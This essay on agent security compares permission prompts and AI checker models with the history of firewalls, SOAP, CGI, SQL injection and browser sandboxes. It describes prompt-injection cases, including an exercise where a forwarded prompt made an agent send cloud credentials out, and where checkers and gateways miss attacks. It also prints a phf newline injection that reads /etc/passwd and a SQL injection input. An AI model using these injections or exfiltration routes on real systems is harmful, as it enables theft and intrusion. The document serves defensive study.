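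Some dangerous actions look harmless even with every detail on display. Suppose a user tells an agent to send an outside auditor only the totals from some invoices. A planted instruction makes the agent copy the full invoices into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send `report.csv` to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name are all fine. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, asked 80 volunteers to judge requests of this kind, along with simpler ones, using four versions of the prompt:

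| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's original limits and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the relevant steps joined into one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

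A person reading the joined statement for the invoice case learns that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The further gain from joining that information into one statement could be chance, since only 20 people used each version.

Better prompts take about twice as long to answer. At 33.2 seconds each, a hundred would take 55 minutes, so a product that asks about every command can't use them. Also, half the requests in the study were unsafe, while real users may approve hundreds of harmless requests before a bad one, so they have much less reason to look closely.

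### From Android to coding agents

Evidence that people ignore permission screens predates AI agents. In *Android Permissions* (2012), Felt, Ha and colleagues studied the list of permissions that Android phones then showed before installing an app. They surveyed 308 users online and watched 25 others in a laboratory. In both groups, 17% paid attention to the permissions during an installation, and 42% of the laboratory group didn't know the permissions existed. Only 3% of the online group correctly answered all three questions about what particular permissions allowed.

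The screens did have some effect. A fifth of the laboratory group could describe cancelling an installation because of the permissions, and Felt and colleagues suggested that such people could warn others in reviews. That doesn't carry over well to agents, because millions of people install the same app, but nobody else reviews a prompt about one command in one person's project.

Android also asked only once per app. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts, up from 93% in its earlier posts. Most commands are safe, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. But the same users reject 39% of the plans the agent shows them before starting work. Although some of them probably just want a different design, they evidently read the plans.

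A more direct test involved 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the researchers replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. Only 13.6% of testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so people guarding their own files might do better, but this doesn't explain the decline within a session as easily.

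Some users also turn off permission prompts. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all permission checks off. Nearly half of active command-line users had written rules that approve some shell commands in advance, and many of these rules allow any Python or Node script, which amounts to allowing everything. In the pre-screening for *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), 13 of 16 people said they chose "Always Allow" just to get rid of prompts. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) warns toolmakers against reading such choices as growing trust, because they may come from habit or pressure to finish.

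### Asking less often

One remedy is to ask only when an action could do real harm. Anthropic reports that prompts fell by 84% in its internal use when it put Claude Code's shell in a sandbox that blocks the network and confines changes to the project folder. Commands that stay inside those limits need no approval. At that rate, a session that once had a hundred prompts would have sixteen, and answering them carefully would take about nine minutes.

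Another way to reduce prompts is to let each answer cover more tool calls, within limits. *Options, Not Clicks* presents ConLeash, which applies "Always Allow" only inside a stated boundary and not to the whole tool. Earlier answers then covered 41.9% of tool calls. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) ties each approval to the exact effect the person saw. On AgentDojo's ordinary tasks, this needed an average of 0.75 prompts per task and blocked none of the tasks, although the approvers were simulated. The paper also shows that fewer prompts can miss an attack split into small steps. An attacker who divided a payment into pieces too small to need approval always succeeded until the researchers added a limit on the total.

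Asking people less often doesn't necessarily make them stricter. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day. The agent attempted 18 actions, and seven of them, such as buying travel insurance or reading private messages, went beyond its instructions. One group had to allow or deny every action. For a second group, a model allowed eight harmless actions and left the other ten, including all seven excessive ones, for the participant to decide. A third group first wrote rules for spending, sending, deleting and private data, choosing from "allow", "ask" or "never".

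| | Asked every time | Model screens first | Own rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Average number of prompts | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Excessive actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
| Total time, including writing rules | 142 s | 120 s | 129 s |

The screening model sent every excessive action to the right person, but people approved 46.1% of them. The rules did worst, mainly because people set 114 of 140 to "ask", which postponed the decision, and approved two-thirds of the excessive actions they were then asked about.

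Some of those approvals may have been sensible. Nearly everyone allowed the agent to call the airport to confirm a flight, and users are free to accept help they didn't request. An 18-action session is also too short to show how people behave after hundreds of prompts. Still, the case for fewer questions depends on people using the attention they save, and Yan found no sign that they did.

### A model that approves

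The other approach is to have a second model decide, as Claude Code's auto mode does. Since August 2026, new sessions on most individual and team plans have started in this mode by default. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) reports that later versions start in it on every plan.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a system in which reading files and editing the project need no review. For most other actions, a checking model first gives a quick yes or no, leaning towards blocking. If it blocks the action, it then reasons at length before making a final decision. A refusal goes back to the agent, which usually finds another way. After three refusals in a row or twenty in a session, a person takes over.

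The checker reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. The agent therefore can't persuade it to make a bad decision, and instructions planted in a web page never reach it directly. But the checker sometimes can't determine where a value came from. If the agent deletes job abc123, the checker can't determine whether the agent looked up that ID or guessed it.

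| | Safe actions blocked, of 10,000 | Real overreach missed, of 52 | Simulated data theft missed, of 1,000 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick check alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both checks | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second check prevents about 800 needless refusals in 10,000 actions, but it lets more harmful actions through. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the checker had identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't agreed to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic calls the 17% miss rate an improvement for people who would otherwise switch the checks off, but arguably a step back for those who review every action carefully.

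Few people seem to do that. In the test with 1,053 people, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, and its block rate didn't fall as sessions got longer. The testers caught only six of the 116 commands it missed, so having a tired person check what the model allowed would have added almost no protection.

Anthropic also cites an outside evaluation in which none of 720 planted attacks succeeded against its newest models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded without a checker, so nearly all of that protection came from the models' resistance to the attacks.

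Independent results on a different kind of mistake are much worse. In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) gave agents 128 operations tasks with underspecified requests. In one, the user asks the agent to remove old experiment files without specifying whose. The agent tries to delete a colleague's files too, and the checker allows it. The checkers in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code approved 54%, 93% and 80% of such out-of-scope actions. They also blocked 10% to 37% of in-scope actions, and the researchers found no statistically significant evidence that the checkers could tell the two apart.

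These figures are consistent with Anthropic's 89%. Its test used commands that are dangerous in almost any setting, whereas deleting old files is normal and becomes wrong only because of who owns them. Of the 143 out-of-scope actions, 132 broke a rule that the user knew but the checker had no access to, because it appeared neither in the request nor in anything the agent had read.

Yang and colleagues then added one statement to each request, for example that the agent may delete only development files that belong to Alex and to one project. They had the checkers judge the same actions again:

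| Checker | Out-of-scope actions approved: before | After | Proper actions blocked: before | After |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

Stronger checking models hadn't produced any such gain. In a common test across nine models, showing the checker the results of earlier tool calls helped only once the request contained the rule, when it cut misses from 9% to 2%. The agents also improved, and none attempted an out-of-scope action in 384 new runs with the statements in place.

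So it may be most useful to ask the user, before the work starts, whose files or which projects the task covers. A model, which doesn't tire, could then apply the answer to every action, and a person would decide only on the few actions that can't be undone. The researchers had an advantage, though, because they took each statement from their grading rules. A real user would have to think of the restriction in advance, and the people in Yan's study mostly put such decisions off. Users may find it easier to answer a question about one task than to set a rule for all spending or all deletion, but none of these studies tested that.

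A user can also authorize an attack unknowingly. In an exercise in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic emailed a colleague a prompt that looked like routine setup work and asked them to run it. One step was to read the colleague's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Anthropic repeated the prompt 25 times, and Claude sent the credentials 24 times. A checker that looks for the user's consent would find it in the user's own message. Anthropic concluded that only limits on which files the agent can read and where it can send data would have stopped the attack.

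## What firewalls and proxies taught

Limits on where data can go are much older than AI agents. Since the 1980s, companies have put firewalls between their networks and the internet to control which traffic may pass. Early designers had to choose how much of each message a firewall should interpret, and they settled on two main designs.

### Packet filters and application gateways

Data crosses the internet in packets. Each packet carries the addresses of its sender and recipient, and a port number that identifies the service it is meant for. Web traffic (HTTP), for example, uses port 80. A packet filter passes or drops each packet according to these addresses and port numbers. It is fast and works with any service, but it can't distinguish a harmless request from an attack on the same port.

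An application gateway uses a program called a proxy, which keeps one connection to the outside network and another to the inside and relays requests between them, so no packet passes straight through. A mail proxy, for instance, can reject a malformed command or a message for an unapproved machine. According to *A Toolkit and Methods for Internet Firewalls*, this design is less flexible because somebody has to write a proxy for each protocol.

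A rule about which websites an agent may contact works like a packet filter. A tool that can only add appointments to one clinic's calendar works more like an application gateway, because its checks can be based on what each argument means.

### AT&T's two machines

*The Design of a Secure Internet Gateway* (Cheswick, 1990) describes how AT&T protected its internal network. Around the time of the 1988 Internet Worm, a program that spread itself across the Internet, a sweep of 1,300 machines inside Bell Labs found more than 300 with at least one known security hole. Nobody could keep every machine secure, so the company needed a barrier in front of them.

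Cheswick decided against a filtering router. He wasn't sure it would stop a clever worm from getting in through the permitted ports, and it kept no log of attempted break-ins. If it allowed outside logins, strangers could guess passwords on every machine behind it.

AT&T's first gateway was a single computer connected to both networks. It kept the worm out because it ran neither of the two programs that the worm exploited. But if the worm had infected the gateway, it could have gone on to the machines inside. The replacement therefore used two computers, on the assumption that the outer one might fall. The outer machine, `inet`, held nothing secret. A private link carried all its inward connections to an internal machine, `r70`, which offered it only three services:

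- a connection to the mail port of an approved machine
- a login, once the user had answered a numerical challenge with a $50 hand-held device
- a connection to a logging service

An intruder who took over `inet` completely, even replacing its operating system's kernel, would still have only these ways in. The better agent sandboxes are also designed on the assumption that the agent's machine is compromised from the start.

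Outgoing traffic was much less restricted. A program on `inet` connected to any internet address an employee named and copied bytes in both directions without checking them.

The gateway still caused employees some inconvenience, because they needed special versions of the login and file transfer programs. Transfers through `r70` ran at 9 to 16 Kb per second, compared with about 60 to 90 on `inet`. Most employees seemed content, though some asked for a chat program and other services that the gateway didn't carry. The design also had three parts that could fail, while a simple router had one.

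The gateway could protect only against traffic that passed through it. When the worm struck, AT&T had a second, unguarded link to the internet, and the company escaped infection only because people at the other end of that link shut down their machines in time. In the terms used for agents, confinement had failed even though the authorization rules were sound.

### Everything moves to port 80

Firewalls typically blocked most ports, but nearly all of them let web traffic through. *On the use of HTTP as a Substrate* (Moore, 2002) explains that each new protocol needed an administrator's explicit permission and sometimes a firewall upgrade, so designers had a strong incentive to send their traffic inside web requests instead.

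SOAP, a protocol that let a program on one computer call functions on another, is the best-known case. Older protocols of this kind used port numbers assigned at run time, so firewalls blocked them. Chappell (1999), in *Simple Object Access Protocol (SOAP)*, gives the example of an online bookshop. The customer's software sends an ordinary web request to port 80, and its body calls a function named `PlaceOrder` with a title and an author. If the shop also offered a function that deleted a customer's account, a packet filter couldn't tell the two calls apart.

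The security writer Bruce Schneier objected that firewalls had good reasons to block such calls from strangers. Schneier (2000), in *Crypto-Gram*, quotes Microsoft as saying that one advantage of SOAP was not having to persuade administrators to open more ports. Two years later he told a conference that SOAP was "firewall-friendly" in the way that a bullet is "skull-friendly". Udell (2013), in *Friendly firewalls*, recalls the remark and adds that it was equally true of REST, the simpler style that most web services use.

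SOAP's defenders could fairly reply that nothing tied it to the web's port. The developer who writes the blog intertwingly, for example, ran it on port 5049. *SOAP protocol review*, a message from June 2000, asked the designers to give SOAP its own port. Moore likewise recommended separate ports for substantially new services, and rejected evading a site's security policy as a reason to use HTTP. In 2022, the IETF's *BCP 56, RFC 9205 on Building Protocols with HTTP* announced guidance to replace this advice. The new guidance treats building on HTTP as common practice and explains how to do it well.

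Gaynor and Bradner (2001) parodied the trend in *Firewall Enhancement Protocol (FEP)*, a mock standard published on 1 April 2001. The protocol puts entire internet packets inside web requests so that any application can cross any firewall without the administrator's help. They argue that this does no harm because firewalls exist to stop outsiders and "ignore threats from within". Bradner (2001), in *Almost a joke*, reports that a number of readers found the parody uncomfortably close to the truth.

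The problem can be stated exactly. Split each message into a part h that the firewall examines and a part b that it doesn't. A rule that permits h permits every effect in

E(h) = { effect(h, b) : b is anything the receiver accepts }

While port 80 led only to programs that returned web pages, E(h) was small, and a rule about port 80 limited what could happen. Once servers accepted function calls in the same kind of request, E(h) grew to include whatever those functions could do. The same firewall rules now limited less, because their value had always depended on the programs behind the port, which other people could replace.

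The rules still blocked traffic on every other port, but they now showed little about the traffic they allowed. A tool list that contains a shell, or the `execute` tool in Cloudflare's Code Mode, has the same weakness. For Code Mode, the main pressure came from the cost of tokens, not from administrators who withheld permission.

### Jobs that only the endpoints can finish

A firewall can try to recover some meaning by examining more of each message, but this has limits. Saltzer, Reed and Clark (1984) argue in *End-to-End Arguments in System Design* that some functions can be complete and correct only with the help of the applications at the two ends. A partial version in the network between them may improve performance, but it can't replace the check at the ends.

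Their main example is copying a file from one computer to another. The first computer reads the file from its disk and sends it over the network, and the second receives it and writes it to its own disk. Errors can occur at any of these steps, so a network that never loses or changes a packet prevents only some of them. The receiving program still has to read the finished copy back from the disk, compute a checksum (a short number that depends on the whole file) and compare it with the original's. This check also catches the network's errors.

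A network at M.I.T. checked every packet on each hop between gateways, so programmers assumed transfers were reliable. But nothing protected the data inside a gateway. One faulty gateway swapped a pair of bytes about once in every million bytes and damaged source files of an operating system. Their owners had to compare the files by hand with old listings.

Checks in the middle can still save a great deal of work. If a network loses one packet in a hundred, a file of n packets arrives whole with probability

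0.99ⁿ

That is 37% for 100 packets and less than 1% for 500, so a program that checked only at the end would spend most of its time resending long files.

The argument also applies to duplicate requests from agents. A network can discard a duplicate packet, but if an application times out and repeats its request, the network treats the second request as new. In the earlier example of the invoice paid twice, the gateway receives two valid requests, and only the payment service can determine whether the first payment went through.

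Saltzer and colleagues prefer that applications encrypt their own data, because then nobody has to trust the network with the keys. But they leave one security job to the network, which is to automatically encrypt everything that leaves so that a misbehaving program can't deliberately expose information to outsiders. An application can't do this job because it may be the program that is misbehaving.

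The same exception covers much of what a mediating layer does for agents. The end-to-end argument usually assumes that both ends are trying to complete the exchange properly, but an agent that has read a planted instruction may not be, so its own checks offer little protection. The receiving service may be unable to tell that the user never asked for the message, and if the destination is Eve's website, the attacker controls it. The mediating layer then has to refuse the message, even if it has incomplete information.

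Two replies from around 2000 tried to define a reasonable role for such checks. Freed's *Behavior of and Requirements for Internet Firewalls* (RFC 2979, 2000) allows a firewall to act as an endpoint and support only a safe subset of a protocol, but requires that it not cause unintended failures in legitimate traffic that follows the standards. Under a similar rule for agents, if a mediating layer accidentally broke an ordinary task, that would count as a defect in the layer.

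Bellovin's *Distributed Firewalls* (1999) proposes moving enforcement from a central firewall to individual computers. An administrator still writes one policy for the whole organization, but each computer applies it to its own traffic and identifies other machines by cryptographic certificates instead of their place in the network. Each computer can use information that a distant firewall lacks, such as whether one of its programs requested an incoming connection. It can also apply the policy to traffic from colleagues' machines, which never passes through the company's firewall.

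Bellovin's design is vulnerable to a hostile program that takes over the computer, since the program can then switch off the policy. Placing the monitor outside the agent's virtual machine, as in KAIROS, partly avoids this, because the agent can't alter the monitor without breaking out of the virtual machine.

### Encryption and frozen protocols

Encryption made it much harder for firewalls and proxies to read the traffic passing through them. Veillard (2002) preserves part of an argument between software developers about Schneier's criticism of SOAP. One blamed firewalls that let HTTP through without examining it further, and another answered that people used HTTPS, the encrypted form of HTTP, to prevent such examination. A firewall that can't decrypt a connection can detect little more than roughly where it goes and how much data it carries.

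KAIROS's proxy can decrypt the agent's traffic, but it then holds passwords and private messages in readable form, so it needs at least as much protection as the agent's own data. Saltzer and colleagues had raised the same concern about trusting the network with encryption keys.

Inspecting traffic between endpoints also makes protocols harder to change. Carpenter and Brim's *Middleboxes* (2002), published as RFC 3234, catalogues devices that do more than forward packets, including firewalls, caches and load balancers, and warns that protocols designed without them in mind may fail when traffic passes through them. A device that rejects whatever it doesn't recognize will block a new protocol feature even if both endpoints support it.

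Engineers call the result ossification. Thomson and Pauly's *Long-Term Viability of Protocol Extension Mechanisms* (RFC 9170, 2021) explains how it happens. A protocol may allow for future values in some field, but if nobody uses them for years, programmers write software that fails when one appears. TLS, the protocol that encrypts web traffic, had this problem with its version number, so version 1.3 has to put 1.2 in the old field and its real version elsewhere.

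One remedy is to send meaningless values regularly, so that software that can't ignore them fails early and somebody fixes it. Another is to encrypt as much of the protocol as possible, so that devices in the middle can't come to depend on it, but this also hides details that security monitors need to check.

Agent gateways can cause similar failures. *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28* (Körbächer, 2026) describes one in which a gateway strips the response header where an MCP server names a missing scope, so the client is refused and cannot learn what to request. A gateway can also miss an error if it looks for an outdated code. The July revision changed the error code for mismatched headers from -32001 to -32020, and Körbächer found the old number still in some documentation.

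A gateway can also spread an error to many agents at once, much as the faulty machine at M.I.T. damaged one file after another. The July revision lets servers mark their tool lists as safe to share, so a gateway can keep one copy for all clients. Körbächer points out that if someone plants an instruction in that copy, every client receives the instruction until the copy expires.

### A label on the outside of the call

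SOAP's designers gave firewall administrators a partial solution. Each request could carry a SOAPAction header declaring the call's purpose, so a firewall could filter calls without reading their contents. *SOAP security and external underwear* (Udell, 2002) quotes the specification's statement that firewalls could use the header this way.

Nottingham (2001), in *SOAP/XML Protocol and filtering, etc*, asked network engineers whether a header naming the function being called would help them. Dawes (2001) replied that an attacker could put a harmless name in the header and a different function in the body. The firewall would permit the call because of its header, but the server might act on the body. Dawes wanted a proxy that read the same information as the server.

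Fisk (2001) stated this as a general rule that a filter has to interpret traffic the same way the receiver does. If a firewall blocks programs by their declared type, somebody can get a program through by labeling it as a picture. This does no harm if the receiver also goes by the label, because it will try to display the program as a picture. But if the receiver goes by the file's name, it may run the program the firewall was meant to block.

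Udell compared SOAPAction to a scene in the film *Bananas*, in which a new dictator orders everyone to wear their underwear on the outside so it can be checked. He thought companies would have to list every function they offered and inspect the calls themselves. By September 2001, a draft of the next SOAP standard, *(part 2) 6.1.1 The SOAPAction HTTP Request Header Field*, had made the header an optional hint.

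MCP's July 2026 revision brings the idea back. Every MCP request over the web must now name its method in a header, and a tool call must also name the tool. In the inbox example, the call that forwards the mail to Eve would carry these two lines:

```
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: send_email
```

According to Model Context Protocol, whose proposal introduced the headers, gateways previously had to decrypt each request and parse its whole body to find the tool's name. They still have to decrypt the request, because HTTPS encrypts the headers too, but they no longer have to parse the body.

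Suppose a gateway permits `read_file` and forbids `delete_file`. An attacker puts one name in the header and the other in the body, in whichever order might get a deletion past the gateway. The outcome depends on which name each machine uses:

| The gateway reads | The server | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The header | Runs the tool named in the body | The file is gone |
| The body | Runs the tool named in the header | The file is gone |
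| The header | Compares the two names first | The server refuses |
| The body | Runs the tool named in the body | The gateway refuses |

coheigea (2012) reports a flaw of the kind in the second row in Apache CXF, a popular toolkit for web services. In some cases, CXF chose the function from the SOAPAction header without checking the body. The attack worked only between functions that took the same types of argument, and the developers fixed the flaw. Reading the full body therefore gives no protection if the server chooses the function from the header.

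MCP requires the arrangement in the third row. Under Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026), a server that processes a request's body must reject the request if its headers don't match the body. This improves on SOAP's header but leaves some gaps.

Servers that follow an older revision don't have to check that a request's headers match its body. Körbächer warns that a client using the November 2025 revision can send unchecked headers and bypass the gateway's rules. A gateway therefore has to check the protocol version first, then either refuse requests that use an older revision or read their bodies.

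The server's operator also has to be honest. A malicious operator who wants the user's data has no reason to reject a request with a misleading label. A rule based on headers can protect a company's own servers from a hijacked agent, but it can't stop the agent from passing secrets to an attacker's server.

Headers can hold only a limited set of characters, so MCP encodes values that contain any others. A rule that checks for the region "São Paulo" won't match unless the gateway decodes the header first.

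For sensitive operations, Tigera's *The New MCP Headers Are a Gift to Gateways* recommends using headers to refuse calls quickly but reading the body before allowing them. This is sensible because refusing a call based on its header won't block any legitimate calls. If the header names a forbidden tool, either the body names the same tool and the call is forbidden, or the body names a different tool and the server would have rejected the call for the mismatch.

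Even truthful headers leave out much of what matters. The specification's example is a database tool, `execute_sql`, that copies the region into a header but leaves the query in the body. A query that reads one row and one that deletes a table would have identical headers. Körbächer's sample rule uses the headers to limit each customer to ten `execute_sql` calls a minute and to ban the tool in one region for test machines.

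A server's author could also have the recipient's address copied into a header, which would let the gateway block Eve. But the MCP specification advises authors not to expose personal information this way, because every proxy along the route can read and log it. An email address is personal information, so the argument the gateway most needs to stop the theft probably won't be in a header.

### An insider that tries again

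Firewalls mostly guard against outsiders, but an agent works behind them with valid rights to mail, files and services. Cheswick acknowledged that employees could easily bring in harmful programs, and Fisk thought a malicious insider could always hide traffic inside something permitted. Gaynor and Bradner's joke protocol needs only a cooperating machine behind the firewall, and prompt injection gives an outsider that cooperation.

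Ranum's *A Network Firewall* describes early gateways at the computer company Digital whose main purpose was to prevent unauthorized or unnoticed leaks. They did not restrict incoming data. An agent's operator needs to watch traffic in both directions, because an attack can bring malicious instructions in and send stolen data out.

The Internet Worm also had a fixed set of methods. AT&T's gateway ran neither of the programs the worm attacked, which was enough to stop it. An agent can try another tool after a refusal, which helps in ordinary work. But an agent that is under an attacker's influence, or merely persistent, can try the permitted routes until one works, and it may soon find a gap that a worm would never have found.

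Operators of agents have some advantages over AT&T. AT&T had to watch constantly for new, unguarded links to the internet, but an agent inside a sound virtual machine can't add one. Nobody has to persuade an agent to accept slow transfers or an unfamiliar program. The operator can also erase the agent's machine after every task. A gateway for agents can therefore be stricter than one AT&T's employees would tolerate, if someone can list the requests the work requires.

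## What browsers and web programs taught

Web servers have been able to run programs in response to strangers' requests since 1993, and browsers have been able to run programs from strangers' web pages on the reader's own computer since 1995. Firewalls let most of this traffic through, so servers and browsers needed their own limits.

### Programs that any visitor could start

The Common Gateway Interface (CGI) lets a web server answer a request by running a program. As Robinson and Coar (2004) explain in *The Common Gateway Interface (CGI) Version 1.1*, the server chooses the program from the web address, passes it the details of the request and returns the program's output to the visitor. Most servers ran these programs under the same user account as the server itself, so a faulty program could damage the server's settings, documents and logs.

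One such program, `phf`, searched a directory of people. It added the visitor's text to the end of a command and gave the result to the server's shell. In simplified form, a search for Smith produced this:

```
/usr/local/bin/ph -m smith
```

Some characters end one shell command and start another, so `phf` neutralized 20 special characters, including semicolons and ampersands. It missed the newline. A visitor who sent a newline and a second command got both:

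```
/usr/local/bin/ph -m smith
cat /etc/passwd
```

The second line prints the server's list of user accounts. According to CERT Coordination Center's *phf CGI Script fails to guard against newline characters* (2001), attackers exploited the flaw widely in 1996 and 1997. A later version added the newline to the list of dangerous characters. CERT instead recommends permitting only characters that the program is known to handle, which is another application of Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults.

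### Sending the command before the data

Databases had the same weakness, and Kerner (2013), in *Jeff Forristal, also known by the alias Rain Forrest Puppy*, dates the first public discussion of it to 1998. Suppose a webmail site lets Alice search her mail by sender. It inserts whatever she types into a command in SQL, the standard database language:

```sql
SELECT body FROM mail
WHERE owner = 'alice' AND sender = 'bob'
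```

If she types `bob' OR 'a'='a` instead of `bob`, the quotation mark ends the name early and the rest becomes part of the command:

```sql
SELECT body FROM mail
WHERE owner = 'alice' AND sender = 'bob' OR 'a'='a'
```

Since 'a' always equals 'a', the database returns every user's mail. This is SQL injection.

A parameterized query prevents it by sending the command and the data separately. The site first sends the command with placeholders:

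```sql
SELECT body FROM mail
WHERE owner = ? AND sender = ?
```

The database works out the structure of this command before it receives the two values, so it looks for a sender whose name is literally `bob' OR 'a'='a` and finds nobody. The site doesn't need a list of dangerous characters, which could be incomplete.

The popular database MySQL added this feature in 2004. Twenty years later, CISA and the FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) still urged software makers to use it, after attacks through one file-transfer product affected thousands of organizations. The two US agencies want development libraries to make the safe method the default, so that security doesn't depend on each programmer remembering to use it.

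Parameterized queries don't check whether a value is appropriate. If a shop lets customers cancel orders by number and doesn't check who placed them, a customer can cancel a stranger's order even when the query keeps commands and data separate. *Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems* (2026) points out that logins and access control remained hard problems after developers adopted parameterized queries.

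### Why language models have no equivalent

A tool call already separates commands from data. In the inbox example, the mail tool receives the recipient and the body as separate values, so nothing in the body can change the recipient. The model's input lacks this separation, because the model reads the user's request and Eve's email as one stream of text.

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) explains how prompt injection differs from SQL injection. A parser can tell a command from a value in SQL because SQL has a grammar. Natural language has no grammar that separates the two, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they appear. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre adds that a model only predicts the next token. Developers can make attacks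 harder by putting markers around untrusted text, but the model still has to interpret the markers along with the rest of the text.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that attacks cannot be perfectly prevented in models that represent instructions and data in the same space with no enforced boundary between them. The proof doesn't establish whether a different architecture could provide such a boundary, or how often attacks succeed against any particular model.

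Even a perfect boundary between data and instructions would not suit every task. A name typed into a search box should never act as a command, but the inbox assistant has to follow the list in Alice's email. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* observes that such cases need a policy for identifying the instructions in the data and determining which ones the agent should follow.

The closest equivalents to parameterized queries therefore operate outside the model. FIDES, for example, fills in its variables after the planner has chosen a call, much as a database fills in the question marks in a query. David C also recommends a simpler rule from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: a model reading someone's text should have only that person's privileges. Under this rule, the inbox assistant would lose access to the user's Slack once it had read strangers' mail, so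 it couldn't post the summary.

### Java applets and ActiveX

Java applets, small programs that a web page could start inside the user's browser, raised the opposite problem of running a stranger's program on the user's machine. Netscape's browser gave all applets the same narrow rights. An applet couldn't access the user's files and could open network connections only to the server it came from.

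Dean, Felten and Wallach (1996), in *Java Security*, found several ways around these limits. One exploited the domain name system, which translates names such as `example.com` into numerical addresses. To enforce the rule on connections, the browser did the following:

1. It looked up the addresses of the server that had supplied the applet.
2. It looked up the addresses of the machine that the applet wanted to contact.
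3. If the two lists had any address in common, it allowed the connection.

The applet could ask for a name in the attacker's domain, so the attacker's machine answered the second lookup. That machine could reply with two addresses, those of the applet's home server and a computer inside the victim's company. The lists then had an address in common, so the applet passed the check and could attack the company's computer from behind the firewall. The policy was sound, but the check relied on information from the attacker.

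Java's SecurityManager was supposed to be a reference monitor, but Dean and colleagues concluded that it met none of Anderson's three requirements for one. If a programmer forgot to call it before a dangerous operation, the operation went ahead unchecked. An applet could exploit another flaw to change the monitor's variables. Nobody could verify the monitor, because Java had no precise definition.

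Microsoft's alternative, ActiveX, relied on trust in the publisher. An ActiveX control was an ordinary Windows program that a web page could prompt the browser to install. A digital signature identified the publisher, and if the user accepted the control, it ran with all the user's rights. The signature showed that nobody had altered the program since the publisher signed it, but it didn't limit what the program could do. Even a control from an honest publisher could contain a flaw that a hostile page could exploit. People who install an MCP server from a known company on their own computer trust the publisher in much the same way, unless they run the server in a sandbox.

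The applet's fixed limits were safer but ruled out many useful programs. A game couldn't save its high scores, for example. Netscape then let programs ask for individual privileges, as *Politeness Pays as Secure Java Asks for Privileges* (1996) describes. A game could get access to its score file but not to the user's bank statement. Wallach, Balfanz and colleagues also argued, in *Extensible Security Architectures for Java*, for systems that could add new policies after release instead of holding every program to a single policy.

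### The same-origin policy and its exceptions

Browsers also had to protect websites from each other, because a user may have a bank and a hostile page open at once. They do this with the same-origin policy. An origin consists of a web address's scheme (such as `http` or `https`), host name and port:

o(w) = (scheme(w), host(w), port(w))

A script on one page can read data from another page only if both have the same origin, meaning the same scheme, host and port. A script on `http://www.example.com` can therefore read other pages there, but not those on `https://www.example.com`, `http://example.com` or `http://www.example.com:8080`.

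Some sites want to share data, so browsers later added explicit exceptions through cross-origin resource sharing (CORS). The browser includes the page's origin in its request to the other site, and that site can grant access with a header in its reply:

```
Access-Control-Allow-Origin: https://shop.example
```

If the header is missing or names a different origin, the browser doesn't let the script read the reply. The site that holds the data decides who can read it, and is better placed to do so than the user or the page requesting the data. But the policy mostly restricts reading. A page can still send some requests to other sites, such as form submissions, and the receiving site has to check that the user intended them.

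### A broker that holds the rights

These rules worked only if the browser's own code had no serious flaws. In 2008, most browsers ran as a single program with the user's rights, so a bug in the code that decoded images could expose every file the user owned. *The Security Architecture of the Chromium Browser* (Barth, Jackson and Reis) describes a different design for Chromium, the open-source basis of Google Chrome.

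Chromium splits its work between two kinds of process. The renderer interprets pages and runs their scripts inside a sandbox. The browser kernel acts as a broker. It can access files, passwords and the network, and does so on the renderer's behalf after checking each request. The design assumes that an attacker may take over the renderer completely.

The broker can check a file upload request without an extra prompt. When the user clicks an upload button, the broker opens a file picker and records the user's choice. The renderer can then upload that file and no others. Dean and colleagues had proposed a similar window for saving files in 1996, partly because they expected people to click "Okay" without reading if the browser kept asking.

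Web pages can now do far more than Netscape's applets could, but browsers generally attached a separate permission to each sensitive new power:

| What a page wants | What allows it | How far the permission goes |
|---|---|---|
| Another site's data | The other site names the page's origin | Replies that carry the header |
| To upload a file | The user chooses the file | That file, until the renderer closes |
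| To save a download | The broker writes the file | A set folder, with some file names blocked |
| The camera or microphone | The user answers a prompt that names the site | That device, on that site |

To estimate how much the split would help, Barth and colleagues examined 129 flaws that the makers of Internet Explorer, Firefox and Safari had fixed in one year. Of these, 54 let an attacker run arbitrary code. In Chromium, 38 of the 54 (70.4%) would have been in the renderer, where the sandbox would have limited the damage. Another 11 would have been in the broker. Eight of those 11 came from passing unchecked input to the operating system. More sandboxing wouldn't fix them, because some part of the browser has to pass that input on. Of the five flaws in neither the renderer nor the broker, four involved ActiveX.

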